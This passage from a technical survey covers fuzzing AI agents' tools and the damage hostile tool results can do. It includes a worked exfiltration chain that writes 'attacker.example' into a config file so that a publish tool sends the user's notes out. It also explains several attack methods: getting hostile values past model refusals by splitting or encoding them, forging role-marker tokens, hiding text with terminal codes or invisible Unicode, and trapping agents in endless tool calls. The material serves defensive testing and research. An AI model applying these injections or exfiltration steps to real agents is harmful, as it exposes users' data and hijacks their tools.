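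ToFu's view is reasonable for finding faults in a tool's code, because no input check can make a script-running tool safe without also blocking legitimate scripts. But a hostile web page that gets an agent to run a script can do just as much damage as one that exploits a bug. VIPER-MCP's result is therefore a useful warning to whoever decides which tools an agent may have. They can remove the tool, require approval for each script or run the scripts in a sandbox.

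Relying on a tool's description makes it harder to decide what counts as a violation. If the developer of `write_file` deleted the words "in the project folder", ToFu would have less reason to treat an outside path as a violation, although the code would be no safer. A vague description can hide a bug, and an exaggerated one can make behavior the developer intended look like a violation. Before fuzzing a tool, its developers should write down which files, addresses and commands it may use, and give the fuzzer those limits directly.

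## Fuzzing tools through the whole agent

Direct fuzzing, as in ToFu, does not show whether an attacker can get a hostile value to the tool. An agent-level fuzzer tests this by letting the model choose the tools and arguments, and a successful run produces a prompt that developers can use to reproduce the attack.

### What the model does to a hostile value

Models often change values before passing them to a tool. *VIPER-MCP* (Sun, Kang and colleagues, 2026) describes a server called context-sync that inserted a file path between quotation marks in a shell command, so a path that closed the quotation marks could start a second command. At first the model filled in an ordinary path. When the fuzzer supplied a hostile one, the model made it harmless by escaping the quotation marks and semicolons. The fuzzer needed eight rounds to demonstrate the attack. On another server, lanhu-mcp, the model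 replaced a hostile value with an ordinary project number because a number normally went there.

A fuzzer that called the tool directly could have passed either value in its first call. The extra rounds tested whether the model's usual behavior protects the tool, and in both cases that behavior only delayed the attack.

This kind of testing is slow. Sun and colleagues' fuzzer takes about 15 minutes per server, most of it spent waiting for models, while ToFu makes more than 40 tool calls per second. Results also vary from run to run. In *ChainFuzzer* (Wu, Nan and colleagues, 2026), a model wrote prompts asking agents to use certain tools in a certain order, and the agents did so in only 27% of runs. A model may also refuse a request containing an obvious attack, which leaves the tool's code untested.

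Agent-level fuzzers use feedback from each run to improve the next prompt. *Make Agent Defeat Agent* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) introduced an early one, AgentFuzz. The table compares it with VIPER-MCP and with ChainFuzzer, which looks for flaws that involve several tools.

| | AgentFuzz | VIPER-MCP | ChainFuzzer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input | An agent's source code and the address where it accepts prompts | An MCP server's source code and a running copy | An agent's tools, with their descriptions and source code |
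| Feedback | How close the code that ran came to the sink | Whether the model chose the right tool, and how far the value got | Where the agent departed from the planned sequence of tools |
| Oracle | A test value reaches a sink | A test value reaches a sink and has a visible effect | A test value reaches a sink, usually with a visible effect |
| Tested on | 20 agents | 39,884 code repositories | 20 agents with 998 tools |
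| Confirmed flaws | 34, in 14 agents | 106 | 365, in 19 agents |
| CVE numbers | 23 | 67 | None given |
| False alarms | None | None on 130 servers without known flaws | No figure for the flaws; 17 of 200 proposed tool sequences were wrong |

### AgentFuzz: from a sink back to a prompt

Random prompts would rarely reach a particular line of an agent's code, so AgentFuzz starts at the sinks and works backward:

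1. Static analysis finds each sink and traces the function calls that lead to it.
2. A language model reads the names of those functions, infers what feature they belong to and writes a prompt that asks for it.
3. The agent runs the prompt while AgentFuzz records which code runs.
4. AgentFuzz scores the prompt, then picks a high-scoring one to change and run again.
5. Once a prompt reaches the sink, AgentFuzz puts a harmless test value in it and checks whether the value arrives.

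The score is *F* = 0.5*S* + 0.5*D* − *P*. *S* is a language model's rating, from 0 to 10, of how well the code that ran matches the intended feature. *D* is 1/*x*, where *x* is the shortest distance from that code to the sink. *P* is a penalty that grows each time AgentFuzz reuses the same prompt or route, so that it tries others.

With these weights, the rating can add 5 points, but the distance adds at most half a point until a prompt reaches the sink. Distance is a poor guide because agents look up tools by name while running, and static analysis often can't follow such calls. When Liu and colleagues removed the rating, the number of flaws AgentFuzz found fell from 34 to 27, barely more than the 26 it found by picking prompts at random.

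AgentFuzz can change a prompt in two ways. If the agent used the wrong feature, a language model rewords the request. If the agent used the right feature but a condition in the code blocked the value, AgentFuzz calculates a value that meets the condition. For example, one real tool ran part of its argument as code only if the argument contained the text `source_doc`. AgentFuzz calculated an argument containing that text, found the words in the prompt that had become the original argument, and replaced them with the new one.

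Running the agent greatly reduced false alarms. LLMSmith, which relies on static analysis, found 10 of the same flaws in these agents but raised 332 false alarms. AgentFuzz used an average of 0.69 million tokens per agent, which cost less than $7 at January 2025 prices.

The number of flaws AgentFuzz missed is less certain. Liu and colleagues report that it found 34 of 35 known flaws, but almost all the flaws on that list came from AgentFuzz itself. As a better check, they manually reviewed 83 sinks it hadn't flagged and found one real flaw. At that rate, AgentFuzz would have missed about ten flaws among the roughly 800 unflagged sinks, though a single case is a weak basis for an estimate.

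*Autonomy Comes with Costs* applies a similar method to prompts that make an agent use up its resources. Its fuzzer, AgentDoS, found 36 flaws in 16 of 20 agents.

### VIPER-MCP: confirming static findings

VIPER-MCP first uses CodeQL to look for routes from a tool's arguments to a sink, covering command injection, path traversal and requests to forbidden addresses. A CodeQL alert gives a file and a line, but the fuzzer has to request a specific tool. VIPER-MCP therefore identifies the tool from the smallest function that contains the start of the route.

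A language model then writes four prompts in different styles, such as a request to diagnose a problem. An agent runs them on a copy of the server that records what reaches each sink. Another model call gives each prompt up to 10 points for getting the agent to choose the right tool and up to 10 for how far the value got. VIPER-MCP rewrites the request around the value if the agent chose the wrong tool, and otherwise changes only the value. It doesn't change both at once because that could fix one problem and bring back the other.

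This separation seems to matter. VIPER-MCP triggered a flaw on 120 of 130 servers with known flaws. It did so on only 86 when it used a single kind of change, and on 85 when it couldn't match alerts to tools.

The 120 successes overstate how well VIPER-MCP would do on unfamiliar flaws, because it had itself found the flaws on 67 of these servers. Sun and colleagues attribute the ten misses to types of flaw that it doesn't cover, such as SQL injection, so all ten were probably among the other 63 servers. The miss rate on those 63 would then be about 16%, instead of the published 7.7%.

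The 106 flaws found in almost 40,000 repositories don't show that flaws are rare, because VIPER-MCP checks for only three types and some servers need outside services that weren't available during the scan. Sun and colleagues also exclude tools whose purpose is to run commands. A person apparently has to apply this exclusion, since VIPER-MCP reported exploits of such tools in ToFu's comparison.

### A flaw that takes two tools

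The flaw that AgentFuzz missed was in Devika, an open-source agent. Devika stored the hostile value during one request and passed it to the sink during a later one, but AgentFuzz tests one prompt at a time.

The same can happen with `write_file`. Suppose the agent has another tool, with the description "Publish a note on the team's website":

```python
def publish(note, config):
    address = read_project_file(config).strip()
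    requests.post(address, data=read_project_file(note))
```

Both arguments are file names, and `read_project_file` rejects any path outside the project folder. The user asks the agent to follow an online setup guide and then publish today's notes. The author of the guide has put their own address where the team's should be, so the agent makes these calls:

```
fetch_page(url = "https://setup-guide.example/")
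write_file(path = "site.txt", text = "https://attacker.example/", overwrite = false)
publish(note = "notes/today.txt", config = "site.txt")
```

The last call sends the notes to the attacker. Tests of either tool alone would probably miss this:

| Test | What the fuzzer changes | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `write_file` alone | The path, text and `overwrite` | Every file stays in the project folder, and the tool may save any text, so the test passes. |
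| `publish` alone | The two file names | The files in the test folder contain the team's address or no address at all, so the tool contacts the right site or fails. |
| `write_file`, then `publish` | The text that `write_file` saves | `publish` contacts the attacker's site. |

The fix belongs in `publish`, which should check the address against the team's own site just before sending anything. `write_file` can't do this because it has no information about how another tool will use the text. A direct fuzzer could find the flaw if the tester thought to put a file with a hostile address in the test folder.

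### ChainFuzzer: planning the route between tools

ChainFuzzer looks for such combinations in the tools' code. It starts with tools that can pass their input to a sink, then looks for other tools that could supply that input. It links two tools if one returns a value that the other accepts, such as a web address, or if one saves data that the other can read. A language model removes sequences that make no sense as a task. On the 20 agents, this left 2,388 sequences.

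ChainFuzzer then writes a prompt for each sequence and runs the agent. If the agent skips a tool or uses the wrong file, a language model compares the run with the plan and edits the part of the prompt that led to the mistake. For example, it may add an instruction to create a file before using it. ChainFuzzer accepts a prompt after five successful runs in a row. In a sample of 200 sequences, these repairs raised the share of runs that followed the plan from 27% to 95%.

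Finally, ChainFuzzer puts a hostile value into the prompt or into content that a tool reads, and monitors the sink. Its oracle for network requests checks for connections to internal addresses. It could therefore expose the flaw in `publish` if the hostile value is an internal address, but it might not flag a request to the attacker's public site.

Wu and colleagues report that 302 of the 365 flaws need several tools, but this describes the route the value took. Direct fuzzing might still find some of these flaws, because ChainFuzzer chooses final tools whose own arguments can affect a sink, and a direct fuzzer could sometimes pass the hostile value straight to the last tool. Only flaws like the one in `publish`, where the value comes from a file that an earlier tool wrote, depend on the sequence or on a specially prepared test folder.

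The hostile value came from the user's prompt in 225 cases and from content such as a web page in the other 140. Usually only the second kind threatens someone using an agent on their own laptop.

### When a refusal hides a flaw

Some developers rely on the model to block attacks. Microsoft instructs its TaskWeaver agent that the "Planner must reject the User's request if it contains potential security risks". Liu and colleagues tested this defense by replacing AgentFuzz's harmless test values with harmful ones. All 34 flaws remained exploitable, although 14 needed extra text to get past the model's safeguards or instructions.

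ChainFuzzer responds to a refusal by splitting, encoding or reformatting the value. In one test, the original values triggered flaws in 91 of 500 attempts, and the altered values did so in 443. The sample favors the altered values because it contained only flaws that ChainFuzzer had already confirmed, many of them by altering values. In a fairer comparison, ChainFuzzer found 132 flaws without altering values and 365 in the full test.

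The model that writes the tests can also refuse. When Claude Haiku 4.5 wrote and scored VIPER-MCP's prompts, the fuzzer triggered flaws on at most two of the 130 vulnerable servers. With GPT-5.4-mini, it triggered flaws on 83 to 88 servers, depending on which of five models ran inside the agent. Unlike a refusal by the agent's model, which gives users some protection, a refusal by the test writer only reduces the number of flaws reported.

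Harmless test values avoid much of this problem. If the oracle monitors the sink, a command that prints the number 1 reveals the same flaw as a command that deletes files, and a model is less likely to refuse it.

### Failures without an attacker

Agents can also misuse tools when no one intends harm. *ToolFuzz* (Milev, Balunović and colleagues, 2025) searches for ordinary requests that fail because a tool's description is incomplete or wrong.

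To find runtime errors, ToolFuzz first fuzzes the tool alone. When an input value causes an error, a language model writes a natural request containing that value, and ToolFuzz checks whether the agent triggers the same error. One map tool, for example, rejected queries of 100 characters or more, a limit its description didn't mention. On 32 public tools and a set of purpose-built ones, ToolFuzz found 41 different errors with 3,297 prompts. A simpler method that had a model write test prompts from the tool descriptions alone found 38 with 28,824 prompts.

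Wrong answers are harder to detect because ToolFuzz has no correct answers to compare them with. It therefore sends the agent the same question in several wordings, such as "Find grocery store near San Jose" and "Find supermarket near SJ USA". It reports a problem only if the tool calls differ, the tool's results differ, and the agent's answer doesn't match what a language model predicts. Even with all three conditions, 534 of its 1,156 reports (46%) were false alarms.

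One of the real errors involved PubMed, a database of medical research. The agent asked for papers from 2020 but got one from 2024 because the tool's description didn't explain how to search by date.

Milev and colleagues then had a model rewrite tool descriptions using the failed requests. This raised the share of tasks an agent completed with a set of file tools from 22% to 33%. But a rewrite based only on the description and source code reached 32%, so the failed requests added little. They helped more with a terminal tool. The agent completed 30% of tasks after the rewrite that used the failed requests, and 25% after the better of two rewrites that didn't.

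Li, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *No Attack Required*, test agent skills, which are folders of written instructions, sometimes with scripts, that an agent loads for a particular job. The instructions often contain safety rules. Their fuzzer, SEFZ, turns each rule into a forbidden path through the record of a run. The rule "ask the user before overwriting a file" would become:

```
source: the user's request
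sink:   a call that overwrites a file
gate:   the user's confirmation
violation if a chain of events leads from source to sink without a gate
```

A language model labels the events in each run, and ordinary code then searches for the forbidden path. A run scores one third if it contains the source, two thirds if it also contains the sink, and 1 if no gate separates them. SEFZ uses these scores when choosing how to change the user's messages next. It may make the user's consent vague ("I'm not stopping you"), add time pressure or have the user claim to be the owner.

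SEFZ found violations in 120 of 402 skills (30%). One was a smart-home skill that required confirmation before unlocking a door. Its script tried to read the answer from a terminal, which the agent didn't have, and treated the missing answer as permission. The skill also offered a general command that skipped the check, and the agent used it. In another case, the agent asked for permission to send an email and the user refused. The agent sent it anyway, reasoning that the user had already supplied the details.

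SEFZ tried up to 50 conversations per skill, ran each three times and counted a skill if any violation appeared, so the 30% figure doesn't mean that users will often see such violations. The labels can also cause false alarms by putting two different actions in the same category. Li and colleagues say this was rare but give no rate. They report previously unknown violations in 26 deployed skills, and maintainers or the marketplace had confirmed three by the time of the study.

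Better wording may not fix such rules. A language model had rated every safety rule in 46 of the 120 skills as well written. If the orchestrator's code required confirmation before `write_file` could overwrite anything, the rule would hold however the user phrased the request.

### What each method can establish

| | Direct fuzzing | Agent-level fuzzing |
|---|---|---|
| It finds a flaw | The code mishandles this value, whether or not an attacker can deliver it. | This model, with these instructions and tools, delivered the value. |
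| It finds nothing | None of the values tried caused a violation that the oracle could detect. | The code may be safe, or the hostile value may never have reached it. |

When fuzzing through the agent finds nothing, the result is hard to interpret because the model may have refused, chosen another tool or changed the value. Recording every value that reaches the tool, as well as those that reach the sink, would separate these cases. Hostile paths that the tool itself rejected are useful evidence about its code, unlike requests that the agent refused before calling it.

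Fuzzers that start from sinks are also limited because, as Ananto and colleagues point out, a list of sinks doesn't include a tool's own rules, such as which sites `publish` may contact. To check those rules, an agent-level fuzzer would need an oracle for each tool, like ToFu's.

Some failures appear only when a model is calling the tools. Testing the tools directly would not have caught the email that the agent sent after the user refused, because the mistake was in how the model interpreted the conversation.

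For a flaw like the one in `publish`, the model is useful mainly for finding the sequence of calls. Developers can then save the calls to `write_file` and `publish` and replay them without a model. A direct fuzzer can also vary the saved address, which would test the repaired `publish` with thousands of addresses in the time an agent takes to try a few.

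## What hostile results do to the software that reads them

A tool's result can do damage before the model reads any of it. Suppose an agent has a tool, `fetch_page`, that downloads a page or file and returns its text, and the user asks the agent to save a summary with `write_file`. Whoever runs the website chooses every byte of the download. Several programs then process those bytes, and each relies on an assumption that an attacker can break:

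| Stage | Assumption | How a hostile result breaks it |
|---|---|---|
| Download | The reply comes from the address that the tool checked. | A redirect leads to the user's private network. |
| Decoding and unpacking | A small file stays small. | An archive expands a thousandfold. |
| Parsing | The result has the promised fields and types. | A list arrives as a single string. |
| Shortening | The missing part doesn't matter. | Padding pushes the important part past the cut. |
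| Placement in the prompt | Only the serving software writes role markers. | The text spells out a marker, and the tokenizer produces the real one. |
| Display | The user sees what the model reads. | Terminal codes or invisible characters hide part of the text. |
| Reuse in another call | A value from one tool is safe for the next. | A file name leads out of the permitted folder. |

### Redirects, archives and long files

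A web server can answer a request with a redirect to another address, and many network libraries follow redirects automatically. If `fetch_page` checks only the address in the tool call, a public website can redirect it to a page on the user's private network, or to the internal address where cloud servers get their access keys.

For every address in the chain, the tool should look up the IP address behind the name, reject it if it is private, and otherwise connect to that same IP address, because a second lookup could return a different one. This protects the private network, but a public page that passes the check can still be hostile.

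The usual compression method for zip files can shrink repetitive data by a factor of about 1,000, so a 10-megabyte download can unpack to 10 gigabytes. Limiting the download size doesn't prevent this, and the sizes listed inside the archive can't be trusted because the attacker wrote them. The unpacking code has to count bytes as it writes them and stop at a limit. It also needs limits on the number of files and on archives inside archives.

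The attacker also chooses the file names in an archive. If the unpacking code doesn't check them, a name containing parent-folder references can make it write outside the intended folder, as in the first version of `write_file`. Python's `tarfile` module had this flaw, known as CVE-2007-4559. Its safer extraction filter became the default only in Python 3.14, released in 2025.

PDFs and images need complicated parsers, and a malformed file may crash the parser or even make it run an attacker's code. Von Hippel and Miyazono imagine a company that lets an image model draw start-up pictures for its customers' computers. An attacker might get the model to produce a picture that exploits LogoFAIL, a group of real flaws in the image parsers that run before the operating system starts. The same concern applies to any picture a tool returns.

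A file parser should run in a separate process with limits on time and memory, no network access and no access to the user's files. This limits the damage from a crash or a takeover. The extracted text still can't be trusted, and an attacker who takes over the parser can choose that text freely.

Orchestrators often shorten long results to fit the prompt, which gives an attacker some control over which text the model receives. If an agent runs a hostile project's tests, the project can print pages of harmless text before the list of failures, so keeping only the beginning of the output would remove the failures. The orchestrator should at least include a note in the prompt saying how much text is missing. It should also shorten the text before adding any closing delimiter, or it may cut off the delimiter too.

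MITRE, which maintains the CWE catalogue, advises developers to decode input before validating it and not to decode it twice. If a filter searches for a role marker before a later step converts full-width Unicode characters to ordinary ones, an attacker can write the marker in full-width characters. These pass the filter, and the later step converts them into the real marker.

### Results that break their schema

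In June 2025, MCP introduced output schemas, which describe a tool's result the way an input schema describes its arguments. A server that declares one must return matching data, and clients should check that it does.

The check can prevent serious damage. Suppose a tool returns a list of old files, and the orchestrator deletes them:

```python
for path in result["old_files"]:
    delete(path)
```

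If `old_files` is the list `["notes/old.txt"]`, this deletes one file. If it is the string `"notes/old.txt"`, Python loops over its characters and calls `delete` on each. One of them is a dot, which stands for the current folder. A path check like the one in the repaired `write_file` would accept the dot, because it counts the project folder as being inside itself. If `delete` also removes folders, it will delete the whole project.

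Schema mismatches also happen without an attacker. Woo and colleagues describe MCP-Atlas, a benchmark whose tasks run against real MCP servers, where schema mismatches occur. A hostile server can cause the same mismatches deliberately.

MCP also advises servers to return structured data a second time as text, for older clients. A hostile server can make the two copies differ. If the orchestrator checks the structured copy but gives the model the text, the model receives unchecked content. The orchestrator can prevent this by discarding the server's text and generating new text from the checked data.

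An output schema gives limited protection against a hostile server, because the server writes the schema and can declare one that accepts anything. A string field can also hold any text, so if the model copies a returned file name into a call to `write_file`, that tool still has to check the path.

### Text that turns into a role marker

The serving software puts the result into the prompt, between markers that identify it as tool output. Other markers identify the system message, the user's messages and the model's answers. According to Woo and colleagues, vLLM, SGLang, llama.cpp and Ollama insert the client's tool messages unchanged.

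A tokenizer then turns the prompt into token numbers. If a web page contains the characters of a role marker, the tokenizer may produce the same special token that the serving software uses. The model then cannot distinguish the page's token from a genuine marker.

Willison (2024) shows the difference with the marker that opens the model's turn in Phi-3, a small Microsoft model:

| How the tokenizer treats the marker's characters | Token numbers |
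|---|---|
| As a marker | 32001 |
| As ordinary text | 529, 29989, 465, 22137, 29989, 29958 |

The second row uses an option called `split_special_tokens`. The standard function for filling in a prompt template generally doesn't handle the problem by itself, though Willison hoped it would. In *Nameless Tokenization*, Yang, Jang and Lim (2026) tested 256 widely downloaded tokenizers and could forge a marker in all of them, and in 99.6% of them through that function.

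The option is also incomplete. It affects only tokens that the model's publisher has declared special, and many publishers leave some markers out. With the option on, Yang and colleagues could still forge a marker in 56.6% of the tokenizers. The markers they could still forge were mostly those around tool calls, tool results and reasoning, which matter most to an agent.

### How much a forged marker helps

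A web page that contains forged markers can appear to end the tool result and begin a new message from the user or the system. *ChatInject* (Chang, Jun and Lee, 2025) compared this with the same attacks in plain text on two agent benchmarks. The forged markers raised the average success rate from 5.2% to 32.1% on AgentDojo and from 15.1% to 45.9% on InjecAgent.

These attacks changed both the visible text and the tokens. *Same Bytes, Different Authority* (Zhan, Song and colleagues, 2026) separated the two effects by giving models identical characters, encoded as either special or ordinary tokens. Ordinary encoding uses more tokens, so the special-token prompts were padded by the same number to rule out length as an explanation. On three of four model families, ordinary encoding reduced the attack's success rate on InjecAgent by 39 to 66 percentage points. On Qwen3-8B, the reduction was only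 8 points because the model, while reasoning, still interpreted the forged text as a message. With reasoning suppressed, the reduction was 50 points.

Yang and colleagues found a much smaller effect in one of their tests. A forged user message succeeded 99.9% of the time with special tokens and 92.8% without them. But the models in that test had not been told to distrust the text, and 62.5% of injections worked without any marker. When Yang and colleagues told Llama 3.1 8B to treat the text as data, plain injections succeeded only 4.1% of the time, while forged messages still succeeded 98.3% of the time. Encoding the markers as ordinary text reduced the success rate of forged messages to 50%. The special token seems to matter most when the model would otherwise ignore the injected text.

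Software can also give a result more authority by mistake. Woo's engine GeulPU has an option that copies a failed tool's error message into a user message, because some models recover better that way. The option is off by default, but if an operator turns it on, a hostile tool could place text in the user's role by reporting an error, without forging anything.

### Keeping markers out of the prompt

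Small changes to the markers can defeat a filter that tries to delete them from a result. Chang and colleagues altered 10% of the characters in their forged markers, and the attacks still worked better than plain text on the three models they tested.

Filters also damage harmless documents, such as a guide to a model's prompt format. Yang and colleagues gave models text containing the models' own markers and asked them to copy the text, count the markers or do similar tasks. The models got 2.2% of these tasks right when a filter deleted the markers.

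Developers may also rely on HTML escaping, because many template engines apply it automatically. *Structural Role Injection in Handlebars-Templated LLM Prompts* (2026) tests whether it protects a prompt. HTML escaping replaces angle brackets, so it breaks markers that contain them, but it doesn't change square brackets, which some models use in their role markers.

Yang and colleagues' own method, nameless tokenization, changes the encoding instead of the text:

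1. Make a copy of the tokenizer and remove the table that connects the characters of each marker to its special token.
2. Use this copy to encode all messages and tool results.
3. Insert the real markers directly as token numbers.

The new method prevents any text in a result from producing a special token. Yang and colleagues tried 16,415 altered markers. Without a defense, 27.3% of them produced a special token. With `split_special_tokens`, 5.1% did, and with the new method, none did. On the tasks with marker text, accuracy was 59.9% with the new method and 8.5% with the standard tokenizer. The new method didn't change the encoding of harmless prompts.

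The method requires control over the tokenizer, so it suits people who serve their own models. It also leaves the marker's text in the prompt, where it can still influence the model. The success rate of forged system messages even rose, from 46.9% to 68%. Zhan and colleagues found that an attacker can search for ordinary tokens that the model represents similarly to a special one. On Llama 3.1, replacing the special token's internal representation with that of its nearest ordinary neighbor restored the attack.

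### Image placeholders that crash the server

Some special tokens mark where an image or video goes in the prompt. A message can spell out such a placeholder without including an image. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3409* (2026) describes how this crashed vLLM. The program counted the placeholders and looked up the dimensions of each image in a list. The list was empty, so the lookup raised an unhandled error. In some setups, the worker process then stopped until someone restarted it. The flaw affected versions from 0.6.1 up to but not including 0.20.0.

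In *Token Injection*, a talk at the Black Hat Europe security conference, Ding and Xu (2025) demonstrated similar crashes in two other serving programs. In TensorRT-LLM, the first request corrupted the program's internal state and the second crashed the process that used the graphics processor. Ollama crashed when it tried to access memory outside the permitted range.

Ding and Xu put the text in a user's message. A web page might have the same effect if the serving software encodes tool results the same way. This possibility weakens the response they list from Meta, which classed the problem as users denying service to themselves. By the time of the talk, vLLM, Google, NVIDIA and Microsoft had fixed the problem, while SGLang, Ollama and two other projects had not responded.

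Ding and Xu also built a fuzzer to look for ways to read or change other users' conversations. It found none, but it could not observe the programs' internal state, and they recommend a closer study.

Encoding untrusted text without special tokens prevents these crashes. The server should also compare the number of placeholders with the number of images, in case a special token gets through another way.

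### When the user and the model see different text

Many coding agents run in a terminal, which treats certain character sequences as commands. ANSI escape codes, for example, change colors, move the cursor or clear the screen. If an agent prints a hostile tool result without removing or altering these codes, the attacker controls part of the display.

Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) describes a test on an early version of Claude Code. A tool returned a harmless description of the user's computers, with one line in white text on a white background. The user saw nothing unusual, but the model read the hidden line and recommended downloading software from the attacker's server. Other terminal codes could write harmless text over an instruction, or make a link lead to a different address from the one displayed.

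Some effects don't depend on the model obeying instructions. Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* shows that text printed in a terminal could put a command in the user's clipboard. Most of the terminals tested removed the trailing line break, but in those that kept it, pasting the text would run the command at once. Printed text could also make the macOS Terminal send data to an attacker through DNS requests, without a click.

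Such codes are particularly bad in approval prompts, because the user relies on those prompts to stop a harmful call. Until version 2026.3.25, tool metadata could alter the approval prompts and permission logs of OpenClaw, an open-source agent, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-35651* (2026). Ordinary developer tools have the same weakness. Aqua Security's *CVE-2026-64654* (2026) reports that GitHub's command-line program printed outside content, including text from agent tasks, without neutralizing the codes.

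Trail of Bits recommends replacing the escape character that starts these codes. This stops most of the attacks, but Embrace The Red's tests also include the backspace character, which can hide text without an escape code. Showing every control character except line breaks and tabs in visible form is safer. Embrace The Red uses caret notation, which displays the escape character as `^[`. The orchestrator should change only the displayed copy, because the task may need the original data.

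Invisible Unicode characters cause a similar problem without controlling the terminal. The Tags block of Unicode contains invisible counterparts of ordinary letters. *Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* explains that an approval window doesn't display them, but the tokenizer processes them like any other text. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (2026) found that access to tools helps models decode hidden text, because they can write a short program to do it. Von Hippel and Miyazono cite a real example, the Rules File Backdoor, in which hidden characters in configuration files led AI systems to write malicious code.

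An orchestrator can remove the Tags characters, but removing invisible characters can damage legitimate text. Several Indian scripts need zero-width joiners to display words correctly, and the flag emoji of England, Scotland and Wales use characters from the Tags block. Approval prompts can avoid this damage by displaying a visible code for each hidden character.

### Results that keep asking for more calls

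A hostile server can keep an agent's loop running by returning results that always seem to require another call. Limiting the length of a single answer doesn't prevent this, because each call starts a new answer with its own limit.

In *Beyond Max Tokens*, Zhou, Zheng and colleagues (2026) changed only the text that MCP servers give the model. The tool's description specified that every call include a progress number and a long list of numbers. The server replied that the work was in progress and requested the next step. If the model shortened the list, the server requested the full list again. After a fixed number of steps, the server returned the correct result. An automated search adjusted the wording to make the calls longer.

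Zhou and colleagues tested six models on 464 requests, each needing one tool, in a simulator where the tools returned fixed data. The table shows three of the twelve combinations of model and benchmark, including the largest and smallest increases.

| Model and benchmark | Output tokens, normal server | Output tokens, hostile server | Increase | Tasks completed, normal server | Tasks completed under a successful attack |
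|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral Large, BFCL | 87 | 57,255 | 658-fold | 83.8% | 78.2% |
| Llama 3.3 70B, ToolBench | 260 | 81,830 | 315-fold | 98.1% | 96.2% |
| Seed-32B, ToolBench | 1,298 | 85,037 | 66-fold | 90.4% | 84.3% |

The 658-fold increase is in output tokens, and it is high partly because the normal task was short. Adding the same number of tokens to Seed's normal 1,298 would give only a 45-fold increase. Real agents often do longer tasks, so their increase would probably be smaller, though each request could use just as many extra tokens.

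The attack also affects other users of the server. It raised peak use of the memory that stores ongoing requests from typically under 1% to between 35% and 74%, and roughly halved the speed of other work on the same machine. *Clawdrain* (2026) applies this kind of attack to OpenClaw agents.

The attack is hard to detect because the agent finishes its task and nothing in the text looks dangerous. Safety models that reviewed the whole run flagged fewer than 3% of attacks. Limits on calls and tokens per task capped how much the attack could use, but it usually still worked by using most of the allowance.

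A limit for each tool would be tighter than one for the whole task. A calendar tool shouldn't need thousands of numbers, although `write_file` may need an argument that long. The orchestrator could also save each tool's description when the user approves it and ask for approval again if the description changes. That would expose a server that turns hostile after approval, but not one that was hostile from the start.

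### Why escaping can't stop an instruction

Escaping works when a program follows fixed rules about which characters have a special meaning, because changing those characters reliably changes what the program does. A terminal acts on an escape code only if it receives the escape character, and a JSON parser ends a string only at an unescaped quotation mark.

The sentence "Clear today's notes" contains no special characters, so escaping doesn't change it. Its effect depends on what the model learned in training about such requests. In Yang and colleagues' test, plain injections succeeded 62.5% of the time with ordinary tokenization and 62.4% with nameless tokenization.

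In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) studied how models recognize who wrote a piece of text. They trained a probe, a simple classifier that reads a model's internal activity, to estimate which role the model assigns to each token. The probe still identified the model's reasoning, apparently from its style, when they removed all the role markers from a conversation or marked the whole conversation as the user's.

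Ye and colleagues then hid a command in a web page that an agent had to summarize. Putting "User:" in front of the command made the model treat it more like a real user's message. Across 212 such variations, the more strongly the model classified the command as the user's, the more often it obeyed.

Correct markers help a model recognize untrusted text, but they don't guarantee that it will treat that text as data. A model that follows instructions in a page can still produce a well-formed tool call, so the orchestrator also needs rules about actions, such as requiring confirmation before a tool overwrites a file.

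## Fuzzing tool results, files and web pages

A tester can also fuzz an agent by changing what its tools return. The user's request is ordinary and the agent calls its tools as usual, but test software alters one of the results. An oracle then checks what the agent does next.

### A proxy between the tool and the agent

The alteration usually happens in a proxy, a small program between the orchestrator and the tool. In the basic algorithm from *ReliabilityBench* (2026), the proxy draws a random number for each call to decide whether to inject a fault. It then returns the real result, an altered copy of it or an error message.

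Suppose the user asks an agent to look up a library's opening time and save it in `notes/today.txt`. The agent calls `fetch_page`, and the real page gives the time as 09:00. The proxy changes the page, logs both versions and passes only the changed one to the agent. As the agent continues, the oracle checks every later tool call and the files in the project folder.

This proxy still runs the real tool, so a mock that returns prepared data is safer for tools that send or delete things. *AgentCheck* (Mazumder and Lia, 2026) combines the two methods. It records the real results from one run and replays them in another, altering a result with one of 12 types of fault, so developers can repeat the same fault after changing the agent. If the agent makes a call that isn't in the recording, AgentCheck runs the real tool. In a test with hostile instructions, the agent may make such a call because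 it has started to obey them, so the tools should run in a sandbox.

For files, the tester also has to decide where to make the change. Altering a PDF tests the code that extracts its text, while altering the extracted text is faster but skips that code.

Some faults never reach the agent. In *Loud Failures, Quiet Failures* (2026), two types of fault affected only one tool, and they occurred in 71% and 74% of trials because the agent didn't always call that tool. The study excluded the trials in which the fault didn't occur. Counting them as passes would have made the agents look more robust than they were.

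*Self-Healing Agentic Orchestrators for Reliable Tool-Augmented Large Language Model Systems* (2026) applies the same fault probability to every eligible step, so longer tasks are more likely to encounter a fault. With a probability of 0.2, the chance of at least one fault is 20% for a one-step task and 1 − 0.8⁵, or 67%, for a five-step task.

### Malformed, false and hostile results

An altered result can be malformed, well formed but false, or correct with instructions added. Each kind needs its own oracle:

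| Kind of result | What the agent receives | What the oracle checks |
|---|---|---|
| Malformed | `{"opens": "09:` | Does the orchestrator reject the result, report an error to the model and keep running? |
| False | `{"opens": "11:00"}` | Does 11:00 appear in the file or the answer? |
| Containing instructions | The right time, with a request to empty another file | Does the agent change any file except `notes/today.txt`? |

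The false time passes a schema check and leads to no forbidden action, so only an oracle with the right answer can detect it. An agent that obeys the hostile request may still save the right time, so checking only whether it completed the user's task would miss the attack.

Most tests of malformed results don't need a model, because a fuzzer can send the results straight to the orchestrator's parsing code, as with the converter. Only tests of what happens after the error need one. *Tool-Calling LLM Agents Under Realistic MCP Faults* (2026) also distinguishes bad content from results that arrive late or never, and a proxy can produce late or missing results as well.

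Errors are easier for an agent to handle than false data. Mazumder and Lia tested five agents on 120 scenarios. The best passed 105 and the weakest 77, and most failures involved agents confidently using wrong results. Automatic retries raised the weakest agent's success rate after timeout errors to 100% from as low as 30%. With out-of-date results, nothing indicated that a retry was needed, and the same agent succeeded in only about three or four cases out of ten, whichever fix the researchers tried.

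Ordinary code can catch false results that are internally inconsistent. Daily AI in Testing Briefing's *Synthetic Tool-Return Fault Injection for AI Agents* (2026) gives the example of a delivery date before the order date. A consistency check would miss an opening time of 11:00 instead of 09:00, because either time is plausible.

### How often agents accept false results

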